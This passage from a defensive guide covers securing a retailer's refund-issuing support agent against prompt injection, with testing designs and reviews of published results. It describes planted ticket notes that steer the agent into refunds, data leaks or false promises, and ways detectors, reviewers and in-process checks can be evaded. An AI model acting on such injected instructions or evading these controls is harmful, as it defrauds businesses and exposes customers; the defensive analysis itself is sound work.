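Suppose a review takes $4 of staff time and reviewers catch half of the undeserved refunds. If 2% of refunds around $100 are undeserved, each review saves $1 on average, which is less than it costs. If 5% of refunds around $450 are undeserved, each review saves $11.25 on average. The retailer might therefore start reviewing refunds at $200. It should also review a few smaller refunds at random, because customers who learn the limit will ask for refunds just below it. Emails that send a customer's data to a third party also deserve review, since nobody can recall them.

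An approval has to cover one exact call. If a staff member merely tells the agent to go ahead, a planted note could still change the order or the amount. AWS gives the example of a share sale that the engine permits only if somebody approved a sale of the same stock and the same number of shares within the past hour. The retailer's version would be:

```
permit (
  principal is OAuthUser,
  action == Action::"issue_refund",
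  resource == Gateway::"support"
)
when temporal {
  formerly within 1h Action::"approve_refund"::response{
    eventResource: resource,
    input.order_id: context.input.order_id,
    input.amount_cents: context.input.amount_cents,
    output.approved: true
  }
};
```

The agent calls `approve_refund`, which shows the request to a staff member and returns `approved: true` only if they agree. The policy still needs the ownership and amount conditions from the ordinary refund rule. The retailer also has to lower that rule's limit to $200, or a $480 refund would qualify under it without approval.

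As written, one approval would permit the same refund repeatedly for an hour. AWS has a separate pattern that uses up an approval when the action completes, but two refunds requested at the same moment could both pass before either completes, just as the three transfers did. The payment system should therefore number each approval and accept each number only once. AgentCore also counts approvals, not the people who gave them, so one person could satisfy a rule that requires two approvals by approving twice.

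The approval screen should show the amount, the order total, the photos and any earlier refunds, all taken from the retailer's own records rather than the agent's summary. An agent misled by a planted note might describe a $480 refund as a routine correction. For an email, the reviewer needs to see the full text and the real recipient, because a summary such as "send claim to courier" wouldn't reveal the leak.

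Reviewers tire because the right answer is almost always yes. If 95 of every 100 requests are legitimate, someone who approves all of them without reading is right 95% of the time and finishes sooner. Anthropic's paid testers, for instance, missed even more of the dangerous commands late in a session than at the start. An attacker can exploit this by sending several small, legitimate requests before the malicious one.

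Asking for human review less often helps most, which is another reason to let fixed rules settle everything they can. The retailer can also hold refunds over $200 until the next morning and have one person check the previous day's requests together. Customers wait longer for their money, but the reviewer can much more easily notice the same photo of a broken coffee machine on five orders when all five are on one screen.

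## Testing the layers separately and together

The retailer now has a detector, a set of rules and staff who review the larger refunds. If the first month passes without a theft, the rules or the detector may have worked, the model may have ignored the injections, or nobody may have tried an attack. To tell these explanations apart, the retailer has to attack its own agent with each layer switched on and off.

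### Four versions of the same test

The test runs the same attacks and the same harmless tasks in four versions of the system, usually called arms:

| Arm | Detector | Policy engine | What it measures |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | Off | Allows every call | The model's own resistance |
| Detector only | On | Allows every call | What the detector adds |
| Policy only | Off, with every ticket marked "clean" | On | What the rules stop if the detector misses everything |
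| Both | On | On | What gets past both |

Two of these arms will pay any refund the model requests, so the retailer needs a copy of the system with invented customers, a dummy payment account and a mailbox that delivers nothing.

The policy-only arm needs the "clean" marks because, under the earlier rule, the engine refuses a refund unless the ticket's status is "clean". If the retailer turned the detector off, no ticket would have a status and the engine would refuse every refund, making the rules look far stronger than they are.

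The procedure has five steps:

1. Write the attacks. The five entry points and five unwanted effects listed earlier make 25 combinations, and four wordings of each give 100 attacks.
2. Collect about 150 harmless tasks from real conversations, including angry customers and long tickets.
3. Run every attack ten times in each arm, because a model's answers vary. That makes 4,000 runs.
4. After each run, record whether the detector flagged anything, whether the model proposed the attacker's action and whether the action took place.
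5. Reset the accounts, so that refund totals and session history don't carry over into the next run.

The U.S. AI Safety Institute's *AgentDojo-Inspect*, a public codebase for research on this kind of hijacking, could save the retailer some programming. The retailer would still have to supply its own tools, tickets and tasks.

A hundred attacks that staff wrote by hand are a weaker test than a determined attacker would be. In 14 of the 37 attack papers that Wang and colleagues reviewed, software searches for a wording that works, yet developers still test their defences mainly on hand-written templates. Adaptive attackers have defeated many published defences, so the retailer should add a separate run in which a tester sees each refusal and changes the attack in response.

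### Judging success by what happened

An attack succeeds when money or data moves, or when a customer receives a false promise. The model's reply is poor evidence of whether money or data moved. It may say "I've refunded the $5,000" after the policy engine has blocked the call, or give a polite and correct answer after the model has read a stranger's order. The retailer should check the dummy payment account, the test mailbox and the order system's access log, and read the final reply for false promises.

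A call that waits for staff needs its own category, unlike in LivePI, where it counted as a blocked attack.

An agent that fails at its task can also look safe, because it leaks nothing. For this reason, Singapore's AI safety institute (AISI, 2026) recommends measuring capability and safety separately. The retailer therefore needs the completion rate for harmless tasks alongside every attack success rate.

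In some harmless tasks, the agent's actions should depend on what it finds, such as a ticket showing that the courier has already sent a replacement. Wang and colleagues built the AgentPI benchmark around these tasks.

The number of tasks determines how small a loss the test can detect. For a completion rate p measured on n tasks, the margin of error is roughly

2 × √(p × (1 − p) / n)

At a measured rate of 90%, the 95% margin of error is about five percentage points either way with 150 tasks and more than 15 points with 15 tasks.

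Repeating an attack adds less information than trying a new one. If none of the 1,000 attack runs in an arm succeeds, the 3/n rule suggests a true success rate below 0.3%, but only if the runs are independent. Counting the 100 different attacks instead gives a limit of 3%, which is safer to report.

### The four arms on two real models

Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar (2026) tested this design in *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component*. Their agent had 12 tools, including email, file access and a control for industrial equipment. They wrote 13 tasks, each with an instruction planted in something the agent reads. A separate program compared the actions that took place with those the user's request had authorised, without relying on any of the defences.

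Two of the researchers checked this program by hand on two samples of 100 attack episodes, one sample being from a pilot run. They judged whether the model had proposed the attacker's action, and agreed with the program on 96% to 100% of each sample.

The agent ran on two small open-weight models, Qwen2.5-1.5B and Qwen2.5-7B. It completed 156 attack episodes and 78 harmless ones for each combination of model and defence. The detector was the agent's own model, prompted to classify text, and it always ran with spotlighting. The strongest policy layer used task-bound permissions plus a rule against sending out confidential data.

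| Defence | Attacks carried out, 1.5B | Attacks carried out, 7B | Harmless tasks completed, 1.5B | Harmless tasks completed, 7B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 66% | 86% | 50% | 99% |
| Warning in the prompt | 65% | 55% | 59% | 100% |
| Spotlighting and detector | 10% | 0% | 37% | 100% |
| List of permitted tools | 42% | 67% | 78% | 99% |
| Task-bound permissions | 1% | 8% | 71% | 99% |
| Permissions, spotlighting and detector | 0% | 0% | 44% | 100% |

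The models behind the task-bound permissions proposed the attacker's action in 64% and 84% of episodes, and the permissions stopped nearly all of these proposals. The retailer should therefore record the actions a model proposes as well as those that take effect. A low success rate with few proposals would mean that the model, rather than the permissions, had prevented most of the attacks, and a different model might not.

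All the attacks that passed the permissions belonged to one task, in which the planted text got the agent to put a false statement in a report it was allowed to write. The 156 episodes covered 13 tasks, with 12 episodes each. The larger model failed this task all 12 times, and the smaller model failed it twice. So the larger model's 8% is an average of one task it always failed and 12 it never failed. The retailer's equivalent is the email promising a ten-year warranty, which also would not be visible in an average across all 100 attacks.

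Without a defence, the small model made unauthorised calls of its own in 40% of the harmless episodes. Task-bound permissions blocked these calls, and completion of the harmless tasks rose from 50% to 71% (95% confidence interval 60–79%). Adding spotlighting and the detector lowered completion to 44% (33–55%). The two intervals don't overlap, so the drop is probably real, though its size is uncertain. A model this small is likely to be a poor detector, which may explain the drop, and the 7B model had no such drop.

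On the 7B model, spotlighting and the detector stopped all 156 attacks without the permissions, so the combined arm can't show whether the permissions added anything. Zero successes in 156 episodes is also compatible with a true attack success rate of up to about 2%.

Other features of the test make the defences look better. Aljumaily and colleagues derived the permissions from the same list of authorised actions that the judging program used, so the design partly ensured a result near zero, as they acknowledge. They counted a false report only if it contained the attacker's exact phrase. On the small model, 13% of attack episodes ended in empty or unreadable output that might have hidden an attack. No attack changed in response to a defence.

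The prompt warning made no measurable difference on the small model but cut the attack success rate on the larger one by about a third. A retailer that changes its model should therefore rerun all four arms, including the policy-only arm, because the rules determine which attacks can pass but the model determines how often they do. With identical permissions, the false report got through 12 times on one model and twice on the other.

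### What ten attempts would do

Aljumaily and colleagues also calculated what an attacker could achieve with ten attempts. They took the success rate p for each task, and averaged over all the tasks the chance that at least one attempt works:

share of tasks broken = average of 1 − (1 − p)^10

Behind the task-bound permissions on the 7B model, p is 1 for one task and 0 for the other 12, so the average chance of at least one success is 1/13, or 7.7%, after one attempt or ten. Putting the 7.7% average into the formula for ten attempts would wrongly give 55%. The retailer should keep the results for each attack, because the correct figure can't be calculated from the average alone.

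The results for detection were different. For each defence, the researchers gave the attacker the group of attacks that worked best against it. On the small model, spotlighting with a detector failed on 21% of tasks after one attempt and 38% after ten (confidence interval 15% to 61%). On the 7B model, the failure rate stayed at zero. With only a warning in the prompt, the defence failed after ten attempts on 91% of tasks on the small model and 85% on the 7B model.

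These calculations use fixed attacks and assume that each attempt is independent.

### Testing the rules without a model

The retailer can also test the policy engine without the model by sending it tool calls directly. This covers the worst case, in which the model proposes whatever the attacker wants. One run per call is usually enough because the engine gives the same answer to the same input. Rules that use a detector's score or the session's history need their own tests.

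The calls should include many versions of each forbidden action. Aljumaily and colleagues collected 33 versions that would have had the attacker's intended effect, and checked how many each set of rules let through:

| Rules | Versions let through, out of 33 |
|---|---|
| List of permitted tools | 27 |
| Simple argument checks | 18 |
| Hardened argument checks | 6 |
| Task-bound permissions | 1 |

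The simple and hardened checks cover the same arguments. The hardened checks more carefully handle values written in unusual but valid ways, such as the email addresses and links discussed earlier.

The tests with real models didn't show this difference. The simple checks let through 10% of attacks on the small model and 21% on the 7B model, and the hardened checks let through 9% and 22%. The planted instructions didn't vary the arguments, so the hardened checks had nothing extra to catch. A retailer that tested only the whole system with fixed attacks could approve a rule that fails against more than half of the versions.

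The same test should include calls the engine ought to allow. If the engine blocks a $499.99 refund on an order exactly 90 days old, the rule is stricter than the retailer's policy. A computer can run hundreds of these checks in seconds, so the retailer can repeat them after every rule edit.

### What the simulations add

Aljumaily and colleagues simulated the cases they didn't run with real models. The tools, rules and judging program were working code, but formulas replaced the language model, the detector and the human reviewer. These results show what follows from the researchers' assumptions and shouldn't be mixed with the measurements above.

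The tests simulated an attacker with one attempt, an adaptive attacker with up to 25, and a compromised model that always obeys the attacker and tries every version of every attack. Each episode's harm score, from 0 to 10, depends on its worst action. For example, writing a file scores 3, sending an email scores 5, and sending out confidential data scores 10.

| Simulated defence | One attempt | Up to 25 attempts | Compromised model | Average harm, compromised model |
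|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 63% | 100% | 100% | 10.00 |
| Spotlighting and detector | 7% | 100% | 100% | 10.00 |
| Task-bound permissions | 4% | 8% | 23% | 0.69 |
| Permissions, spotlighting and detector | 0.3% | 8% | 23% | 0.69 |
| Permissions, with approval after untrusted text | 1% | 3% | 9% | 0.26 |
| Approval alone, without rules | 18% | 64% | 100% | 10.00 |

Adding the detector to the permissions cut the success rate of single attempts from 3.9% to 0.3%, but left it at 23% for a compromised model. The 23% is unchanged partly because the simulation assumed that detection could not stop a model that always obeys injected instructions. The simulation does show how little such a model can achieve within the permissions. It succeeded in three of the 13 tasks, with effects such as a false report or a dangerous link in a permitted email. The average harm stays low because the permissions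 block everything the scale rates as severe.

The harm score is useful because a false sentence and a $5,000 payment count equally toward a success rate. The retailer can score harm in dollars where money is at stake and on a scale for everything else.

The 100% failure rate for detection after 25 attempts assumes that detection weakens with every attempt. The measurements with real models didn't support this assumption, since the detector's failure rate after ten attempts was 38% on one model and 0% on the other. In a second simulation without the assumption, spotlighting failed in only about 22–45% of cases under repeated attack, with or without a detector. But the real tests used fixed attacks, so they can't rule out the assumption for an attacker who adapts. The retailer's detector probably falls between these extremes, and only a test with an adaptive attacker will show where.

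The simulation also assumed that a model obeys more often as the attack level rises, but this didn't hold for Qwen2.5-1.5B. Across six levels, it obeyed 4%, 21%, 50%, 4%, 0% and 4% of the time. The levels were different kinds of attack, and one kind happened to work. There were only 24 samples per level, but the pattern is far too strong to be chance. So a detector or model that resists the retailer's most elaborate test attack may still fail against simpler ones.

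The researchers also removed rules at random, giving each an 80% chance of being kept. Average harm with a compromised model rose from 0.69 to 1.62. Adding approval lowered it to 0.80, still above the original 0.69. Finding a missing rule may reduce harm more than adding another layer.

### Approval and taint in the simulation

The results for human approval come only from simulation, and the reviewer is a formula. The chance that the reviewer catches a bad request is

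0.9 × (1 − 0.3L) × 0.93^k

where L is the average number of harmless requests per task and k is the number of earlier attempts and requests. The middle factor can't fall below 0.3. With L at 0.57, the reviewer catches about 75% of bad requests at first and 36% after ten earlier ones. The direction matches the tired testers in Anthropic's study, but nobody measured these particular numbers.

Requiring approval only for severe actions added nothing to the task-bound permissions, which had already blocked all of those actions. Approval helped when it covered milder actions in sessions that taint tracking had marked as containing untrusted text. This cut the compromised model's success rate from 23% to 9% and required 0.57 approval requests per harmless task. For the retailer, staff time does more good reviewing a $300 refund from a suspicious ticket than a $5,000 refund that the rules would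 refuse anyway.

Approval without rules failed completely against a compromised model, because the model could keep asking. Even a reviewer who never tires and catches 90% of bad requests has about a 93% chance of approving at least one of 25. Allowing one request per episode and refusing the rest cut severe actions from 100% of episodes to 17%. The retailer could limit each conversation to one or two approval requests and pass the whole case to staff after that.

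Taint tracking can also fail, for instance if the software doesn't mark a ticket that an outsider wrote. A total failure behind the task-bound permissions only returned average harm to 0.69, the level without approval. A failure could do more damage behind the hardened argument checks, where the researchers tried to save staff time by requiring approval only for the most severe actions in unmarked sessions. When tracking failed there, severe actions rose to 7.7% of episodes, against 1.7% with the stricter requirement. The retailer shouldn't raise its $200 review limit just because the detector is supposed to mark suspicious tickets.

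### What two separate miss rates imply

A buyer often has only separate figures for the two layers. Suppose a detector misses 5% of attacks and the policy engine lets 8% through. If the misses are independent, the share that passes both is

0.05 × 0.08 = 0.004, or 0.4%

If every attack that the detector misses also passes the policy engine, the share is 5%, the smaller of the two figures. It can't be higher. It could also be zero, if the layers never miss the same attack. For 1,000 attacks:

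| | Independent misses | Greatest possible overlap |
|---|---|---|
| Detector misses | 50 | 50 |
| Policy engine lets through | 80 | 80 |
| Both fail | 4 | 50 |
| Detector's miss rate on attacks the rules permit | 5% | 62.5% |

The last row matters most when the attacker knows the rules. An attacker who learns that the agent won't refund $500 will stop asking for $5,000 and send only attacks from the 80 that the rules permit. The success rate can then be anywhere from zero to 62.5%, even though the two separately measured figures are the same.

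The retailer's detector and policy engine will probably catch and miss some of the same attacks. A polite note suggesting a $300 refund contains few suspicious words for the detector to score and no forbidden action for the engine to refuse. An obvious attempt to take $5,000 is easy for both to catch.

The two figures must also describe the same attacks. If the detector's 5% comes from a vendor's collection of prompts and the engine's 8% comes from tool calls that the retailer wrote, their product is meaningless. Both layers need to be tested on the same set of attacks, with a record of which ones each layer missed.

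Even then, small tests provide little evidence about whether the layers miss the same attacks. On the 1.5B model, spotlighting with the detector let 10% of attacks through, and the permissions let 1.3% through. Of the 156 attacks, we would expect 0.2 to pass both layers if their failures were independent, and two if they overlapped completely. None did. But if the true rate were 1.3%, a test of 156 independent attacks would still find none about 13% of the time, so the result doesn't rule out complete overlap.

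### Microsoft's fall from 26.67% to 0%

One such comparison has been widely repeated. PolicyLayer's *Microsoft AGT Proved Deterministic Enforcement. Where the Next Problem Starts*, which credits Microsoft's .NET team, reports policy violations in 26.67% of cases with safety instructions in the prompt and 0% with Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit. PolicyLayer, which sells controls for tool calls, writes that the result "should end the argument" about whether fixed rules are worth the engineering effort.

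The .NET team's post, *Governing MCP tool calls in .NET with the Agent Governance Toolkit*, contains no violation rates. The 26.67% comes from another Microsoft post, *Securing MCP*, which describes the test of 45 adversarial and 15 valid prompts mentioned earlier as an "internal red-team evaluation". That post gives no result for the toolkit.

The 0% figure appears in *Benchmark*, an unofficial copy of the test's description from Microsoft's repository, and on the package page of *Agent Control Plane*, the component tested. Both are the developers' own accounts.

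The 26.67% apparently comes from ordinary code standing in for a language model. According to the description, the arm without rules "simulates an LLM with a safety prompt". The average response time is 0.02 milliseconds in both arms, and a real language model takes thousands of times longer. The description also specifies that the stand-in catches about 80% of direct requests for forbidden actions and 30% of jailbreaks. With 15 prompts in each group, these rates imply about 13 violations, close to the 12 reported.

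The 26.67% therefore probably reflects how the simulation was written, so it is weak evidence of how often a real model ignores a safety prompt. Aljumaily and colleagues measured 65% and 55% with a warning in the prompt, which is better evidence, though only for two small models.

The 0% is easier to believe but less informative. The rules allowed database queries that only read data, and files from one folder. The adversarial prompts were attempts to trigger actions outside these limits, and the 15 valid ones were requests for simple tasks within them, such as reading a file. The developers had also set 0% as their target beforehand. Zero violations in 45 prompts is compatible with a true rate of up to 6.7%, and zero false alarms in 15 is compatible with a rate of up to 20%.

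The test also doesn't cover the split between detection and enforcement. It compares a written instruction with fixed rules and doesn't include a detector. It also uses only prompts, so no attack arrives through a tool result. The 15 bypasses that Rubinlake reports don't contradict the 0% result, because a fixed set of prompts tests only the routes its writers thought of.

### Questions for any claim of this kind

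A retailer comparing products will see many such figures. These questions show how much each one is worth, with the answers for Microsoft's test and for the real-model part of the study by Aljumaily and colleagues:

| Question | Microsoft's test | Aljumaily and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Did a real language model choose the actions? | Apparently not | Yes, two small ones |
| Did attacks arrive through tool results? | No, only through prompts | Yes |
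| What counted as a success? | A forbidden request that the system allowed | An unauthorised action that took place |
| Which arms did the test include? | Prompt instructions and fixed rules | All four, and five variants |
| Who wrote the rules and the attacks? | The developers | The researchers, who also wrote the judging program |
| How many attacks and harmless tasks were there? | 45 and 15 | 156 and 78 for each defence and model |
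| Did the attacker adapt to the defence? | No | No |
| How did the test count calls sent to a person? | No such calls | No such calls |
| Did the defence reduce useful work? | No, on 15 simple requests | Not on the 7B model; the combined defence did on the 1.5B model |
| Has the developer published the prompts and code? | Yes | Yes |

If a vendor can't answer the first three questions, the retailer should leave the percentage out of its comparison. Even good answers to every question are about someone else's agent, so the most useful thing a vendor can offer is a trial in which the retailer runs its own 100 attacks and 150 harmless tasks.

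## The costs of keeping the layers separate

A trial with the retailer's own tasks also shows how much waiting time and staff work the two layers add. Keeping them separate means that one layer can fail without the other failing, people can audit the rules, and the retailer can replace one layer without rebuilding the other.

### What the retailer gains

If the detector goes offline, the policy engine still blocks a $5,000 refund, but only if the two don't depend on the same server, login or permission.

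Policy rules are easier to audit than a detector's score. As InfoQ explains, Cedar gives the same answer to the same request whatever happened before it, and audits rely on this. An auditor can rerun the recorded request for a refund from last March against the rules in force then and get the same decision. For rules that use session history, the auditor also needs the log of earlier events.

Being able to replace a tool matters because this market changes quickly. Agent Security Index, an online directory, listed 102 tools in November 2026, 28 of which had been acquired or belonged to a parent company. It now lists Lakera Guard, one of the detectors that Waibl and colleagues tested, as Check Point AI Guardrails. If a new owner raises the price, the retailer can switch detectors and set a new threshold without editing the refund limit. The retailer can also move its rules to Microsoft's Agent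 Governance Toolkit, though it would have to change the names of tools and customers in each rule. According to Microsoft's *Introducing the Agent Governance Toolkit*, the toolkit accepts Cedar, the language that AgentCore uses.

### Adding up the delay in one conversation

For the kettle refund, a detector might read five texts: the customer's message, the ticket, the order record, the confirmation email and the final reply. The policy engine checks four tool calls.

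The policy checks take very little time. Microsoft reports under 0.1 ms per check when the toolkit runs inside the agent's process. A separate proxy for tool calls adds less than 2 ms per request, according to *Prompts Don't Protect* (2026), so four checks take at most about 8 ms. In the same tests, models told in the prompt which tools to avoid still chose forbidden ones in 4–37% of tasks designed to encourage their use. The small delay is worthwhile because the proxy's control doesn't depend on the model following instructions.

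Detectors vary far more:

- *Defusing Explosive Prompts* (2026) reports up to 2.9 ms on average for an email of 100–500 words, on a laptop. The detector, DeFuse, targets injections that wait for a trigger.
- Oblakov, Sadiekh and Kokuykin (2026), in *HiveTraceGuard-Pro*, timed 15 guard models, including their own. The medians ran from 14.3 ms to 243 ms.
- *Reflex-Guard* (2026) reports a median of 41 ms for one of its classifiers.
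- *Context-Aware Prompt Injection Detection via Small Language Models in RAG Pipelines* (2026) reports a median of 404 ms for a model that writes a short explanation before its verdict.
- Matsuzaki, in *Securing AI agents*, measured six checks by Datadog's AI Guard in one turn of a working agent. They took 1.46 to 2.16 seconds each and 10.4 seconds together.

Applied to the kettle conversation, these figures give:

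| Detector | One scan | Five scans and four policy checks |
|---|---|---|
| DeFuse | 2.9 ms | 22 ms |
| HiveTraceGuard-Pro | 14.3 ms | 80 ms |
| Reflex-Guard | 41 ms | 0.2 s |
| Slowest of the 15 guard models | 243 ms | 1.2 s |
| Small model that explains first | 404 ms | 2.0 s |
| Datadog AI Guard | 1.74 s (average) | 8.7 s |

The totals are rough because the tests used different hardware and texts, and medians don't add up exactly. Published figures can also leave out part of the delay. *Persona Guardrail* (2026), for example, aims to finish 90% of calls within 100 ms, but its measurements exclude time spent in the application and the network. Oblakov and colleagues' own model took 14.3 ms under one server configuration and 33 ms under another. Its speed also didn't make it accurate, as it flagged about 27% of the harmless items across their benchmarks.

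*A Layered Security Framework Against Prompt Injection in RAG-Based Chatbots* (2026) reports that a chatbot's model takes 300 to 2,000 ms to respond. The kettle refund needs five model responses, which would take 1.5 to 10 seconds in total. An extra 80 ms would hardly be noticeable, but an extra 8.7 seconds would nearly double even a 10-second conversation.

Occasional slow scans matter as well. Reflex-Guard's median is 41 ms, but one request in a hundred takes 326 ms or more. With five independent scans, the chance of at least one that slow is

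1 − 0.99^5 = 4.9%

so about one conversation in 20 would have a noticeable pause.

Much of the delay in the slower detectors comes from writing out reasoning. In *A Dual-Hypothesis Reasoning Framework for LLM Guardrails* (2026), a detector that reasons first took 0.66 seconds per prompt, ten times as long as one that doesn't. *Protect* (2025) describes a detector that gives its verdict first, after a median of 65 ms for text, and logs the explanation afterwards so that it doesn't delay the verdict.

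The retailer can also let the model start on a ticket while the detector is still scoring it, and hold back tool calls and the reply until the score arrives. If the score is above 0.9, the software discards the model's work and passes the case to staff. This wastes some computing on those few tickets.

Separation adds very little to the wait, since a combined product would have to run a detector too. The delay is larger if the retailer divides the work between two agents, one that reads tickets and one that pays refunds. Microsoft estimates 5 to 50 ms for each governed message between agents, mostly for checking signatures and crossing the network. Even that is less than the fastest model response above.

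### Gateway or application

A check can run inside the application, at a gateway, or in the system that carries out the action. Gerstenhaber and Johnson, in *How Cloudflare detects MCP traffic and helps secure it*, compare three similar positions for MCP traffic. For the retailer, the differences are:

| Position | What it can see | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Chat application | The whole conversation and every call the agent proposes, including calls to tools on the same machine | Calls from other applications |
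| Gateway | Tool, arguments and signed-in customer, for every agent routed through it | The customer's request, unless the software adds it, and calls that take another route |
| Payment system | Every refund that reaches it, by any route | The conversation, and often which agent made the call |

A detector benefits from seeing the conversation. Matsuzaki, who writes for Datadog, asked two agents to summarise a bug report containing a planted instruction to fetch a secret key. The first agent ran on a managed AWS service, where the developer's check received only the current tool call and so couldn't judge whether it fitted the user's request. The check could still detect the key in the tool's output. In the second test, AI Guard had the whole conversation and flagged the report, the call for the key and the final reply. Matsuzaki had turned blocking off in both tests, so the demonstration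 shows what each check can detect in one attack, but doesn't measure how often it works.

The policy engine needs to sit where the agent can't bypass it. *Governed MCP* (2026) points out that when a program imports a guardrail as a library, one line of code can disable it. Siddique (2026), in *Governance at the Speed of Agents*, describes Microsoft's toolkit as running in the same process as the agent, with no proxy. The figure of under 0.1 ms therefore comes from a setup that is easier to disable. The retailer's model can only request four tools and can't edit code, so the more likely danger is that a developer removes the check by mistake. A coding agent that controls its own process could remove the check itself.

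Agents that run commands also do more than their tool calls show. In Help Net Security's *Sysdig AI Defense puts runtime guardrails on AI agents* (2026), the security company Sysdig reports that about seven operating-system processes run for every action an agent logs. The support agent runs no commands, so the retailer doesn't need to monitor those processes.

For the retailer, the detector fits best in the chat application and the policy engine at the gateway. The payment system should then refuse any refund request from the agent's side that didn't come through the gateway.

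### How a bypass shows

A gateway governs only the traffic routed through it. Gerstenhaber and Johnson distinguish two ways around it. An employee may connect an agent to an unapproved tool server, or connect directly to an approved server's address and skip the checks in front of it.

Cloudflare's product looks for both by inspecting web traffic for a header that newer MCP clients send. If a request carries the header but didn't come through the approved route, the log shows it and a rule can block it. A request without the header could still be MCP traffic, because older clients may omit it. The product also can't detect tools on the same machine or inspect encrypted traffic that it hasn't been set up to decrypt.

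The retailer's old overnight refund script doesn't use MCP, so this search would never find it, but a comparison with the payment records would. The gateway can attach a number to every refund it approves, and the payment system can store that number with the payment. A payment with no number, or with one the gateway never issued, bypassed the gateway unless staff made it by hand.

Comparing totals can miss a discrepancy between approved and paid refunds. If one approved refund fails and the script pays a different one instead, both systems show the same count. The payment system's log may not show what issued the refund either. In *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (2026), systems behind an MCP server receive only the server's identity, not that of the agent that started the request.

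### Attacks that nobody owns

AWS advertises that security and compliance teams can change the rules without touching the agent's code. The retailer might therefore give the rules to its security team and the detector to the chat developers. If a planted note leads to a $300 refund, the developers may consider refunds the security team's responsibility, while the security team sees a payment that the rules allow. Each team can be right about its own component, and as a result nobody investigates the refund.

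One team can also change how the other's layer behaves without knowing it. The refund rule requires a ticket status of "clean", and the detector's threshold determines that status. If the developers raise the threshold from 0.4 to 0.6 to reduce false alarms, a ticket that scores 0.5 becomes clean and its refund no longer waits for staff. The rule's text stays the same, so reviewing the rules won't reveal the change.

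*Agent guardrails, action gates, harnesses, and governance* (2026), an essay on company AI systems, asks who gets contacted when a violation occurs at two in the morning. That person needs access to both layers to tell whether a sudden rise in refused calls comes from a faulty rule, a misbehaving agent or an attack.

The retailer can add an owner to each row of its table of attacks. The support manager, who knows the warranty terms, could own the warranty promise, and the web developers, who control how replies appear, could own the hidden image in a reply. The ticket status also needs an owner, who should approve any change to the threshold.

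### One record for both layers

Suppose a customer asks when a stand mixer will arrive. The agent reads two tickets, and a planted note in the first asks for a $300 refund on the mixer. The retailer pays it. A shared record of the conversation might look like this:

```
conversation 90417, customer A
10:02:11  scan      ticket 7731: score 0.62, flagged
                    (detector 14, threshold 0.40)
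10:02:14  scan      ticket 7745: score 0.08, clean
                    (detector 14, threshold 0.40)
10:02:19  proposal  issue_refund: order 48377, $300,
                    ticket_status clean
10:02:19  decision  D-5581: allow
                    (permit "own-order-refund", rules 31)
10:02:20  outcome   D-5581: paid $300
```

The fault in the handling of ticket 7731 lies in the code that connects the layers. The application passed on the status of the last ticket it read instead of the worst status so far, so "flagged" became "clean" between the detector and the policy engine. Neither layer's log reveals this on its own, because the detector's warning was correct and the policy engine correctly approved a call marked "clean". The change is visible only in the combined record.

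Other incidents leave different patterns:

| What the record shows | What failed |
|---|---|
| The planted text scored below the threshold | The detector |
| No scan of the planted text | The detector's placement |
| A flagged ticket, but a call marked "clean" | The connection |
| Correct facts, but the rule allows more than the retailer intended | The rule |
| Correct facts and an intended rule, but an undeserved refund | Neither layer; the decision needed other evidence |
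| A denial followed by a payment | Enforcement |
| A payment with no decision | The routing, because the call bypassed the gateway |

The record needs as much detail about allowed calls as about refused ones, since the harmful call in this incident was allowed. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes a proxy that logs the result from every layer of its checks for both allowed and refused calls. Microsoft's toolkit offers what Siddique calls a Decision BOM (bill of materials), which reconstructs a decision from several sources and reports how complete the evidence is. Microsoft's audit log doesn't confirm outcomes, so the last line of the retailer's record has to come from the payment system.

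Marking unscanned texts also matters here. In Matsuzaki's sample code for AWS's guardrail, an error in detection-only mode returns the same values as a scan that found nothing. An investigator would then blame the detector for missing a text that it never scanned.

The retailer can protect customers' details by storing only ticket numbers, scores and versions in the record and keeping the text in the ticket system, where the usual access rules apply. It also needs to keep each ticket exactly as the detector read it, or nobody can reproduce the score.

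### The case for a single product

In the mixer incident, both layers worked, but the retailer's code connecting them failed. With a single product that scores the text, stores the result and enforces the rules, the retailer would have less of that code to get wrong. The product could also provide one log and one place to change settings, which matters to a shop with two developers.

Vendors are moving in this direction. In AgentCore, AWS lets a single policy combine a refund limit, the session's history and a detector's score. In *Our Vision for Securing the AI Agents Your Business Builds*, Akamai's Mani Sundaram argues for one record per agent, covering whom it acts for, what it can reach and whether its behaviour matches its purpose. Sundaram objects that separate guardrails each check only the current conversation. Akamai is selling the alternative, but the mixer incident shows that the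 problem is real.

However, parts of a combined product can fail together. In the AWS setup that Jinno tested, the gateway can call the detector only if its account has a particular permission. An administrator who removes that permission while tidying up could therefore disable every rule that needs the detector's score. A stolen administrator password could be worse if it lets someone raise both the detector's threshold and the refund limit.

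But a single interface doesn't have to create a single point of failure. The retailer can use one screen and one log while running the detector and the policy engine as separate services with separate permissions. Help Net Security's *Obsidian expands AI agent security with runtime policy enforcement* (2026) describes a product partly built this way. Security teams write policies once, a central engine makes the decisions, and several enforcement points, including gateways that customers run themselves, carry out those decisions. The enforcement points still depend on the central engine, so each has to block risky calls if the engine doesn't respond.

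Before buying a combined product, the retailer can test whether its parts fail separately:

1. Stop the detector and propose a $5,000 refund. The engine should still refuse it.
2. Stop the policy engine and propose a $64 refund. No payment should go out.
3. Remove the gateway's permission to call the detector. Rules that don't use a score should work as before.
4. Log in as someone who manages the detector and try to change the refund limit. The product should refuse.

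If the product passes, combining the layers is probably the better choice for a small retailer. But it would be a mistake to enforce the refund limit only in the combined product. The payment system can enforce its own $500 limit on refunds from the agent, so that an error in the product can't remove the last control.

### When one layer is enough

A chatbot that answers questions from public help articles has no tool calls to check, so it needs only a guardrail. *Securing LLM-as-a-Service for Small Businesses* (2026) describes a platform for such chatbots that relies on text-level defences. Carefully written prompt instructions caught 99.6–100% of the attacks in its tests, but only after repeated manual tuning for the scenario. That result is far better than the one Aljumaily and colleagues measured with a prompt warning, and a retailer shouldn't expect it from a first draft of the instructions.

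Even this chatbot needs ordinary software controls. Its search must cover only documents the customer is allowed to read, and the application must remove untrusted images from its replies.

A fixed workflow doesn't need a policy engine for the agent if its actions never depend on the model's output. Suppose a retailer's warehouse scans a returned parcel, ordinary code refunds the price, and a model writes a summary for staff. An injection can spoil the summary but can't change the refund. If the model instead sorts returns into "refund" and "reject", its output decides who gets a refund. The retailer then needs a fixed limit on what the "refund" label can trigger, even though the model never proposes a tool call.

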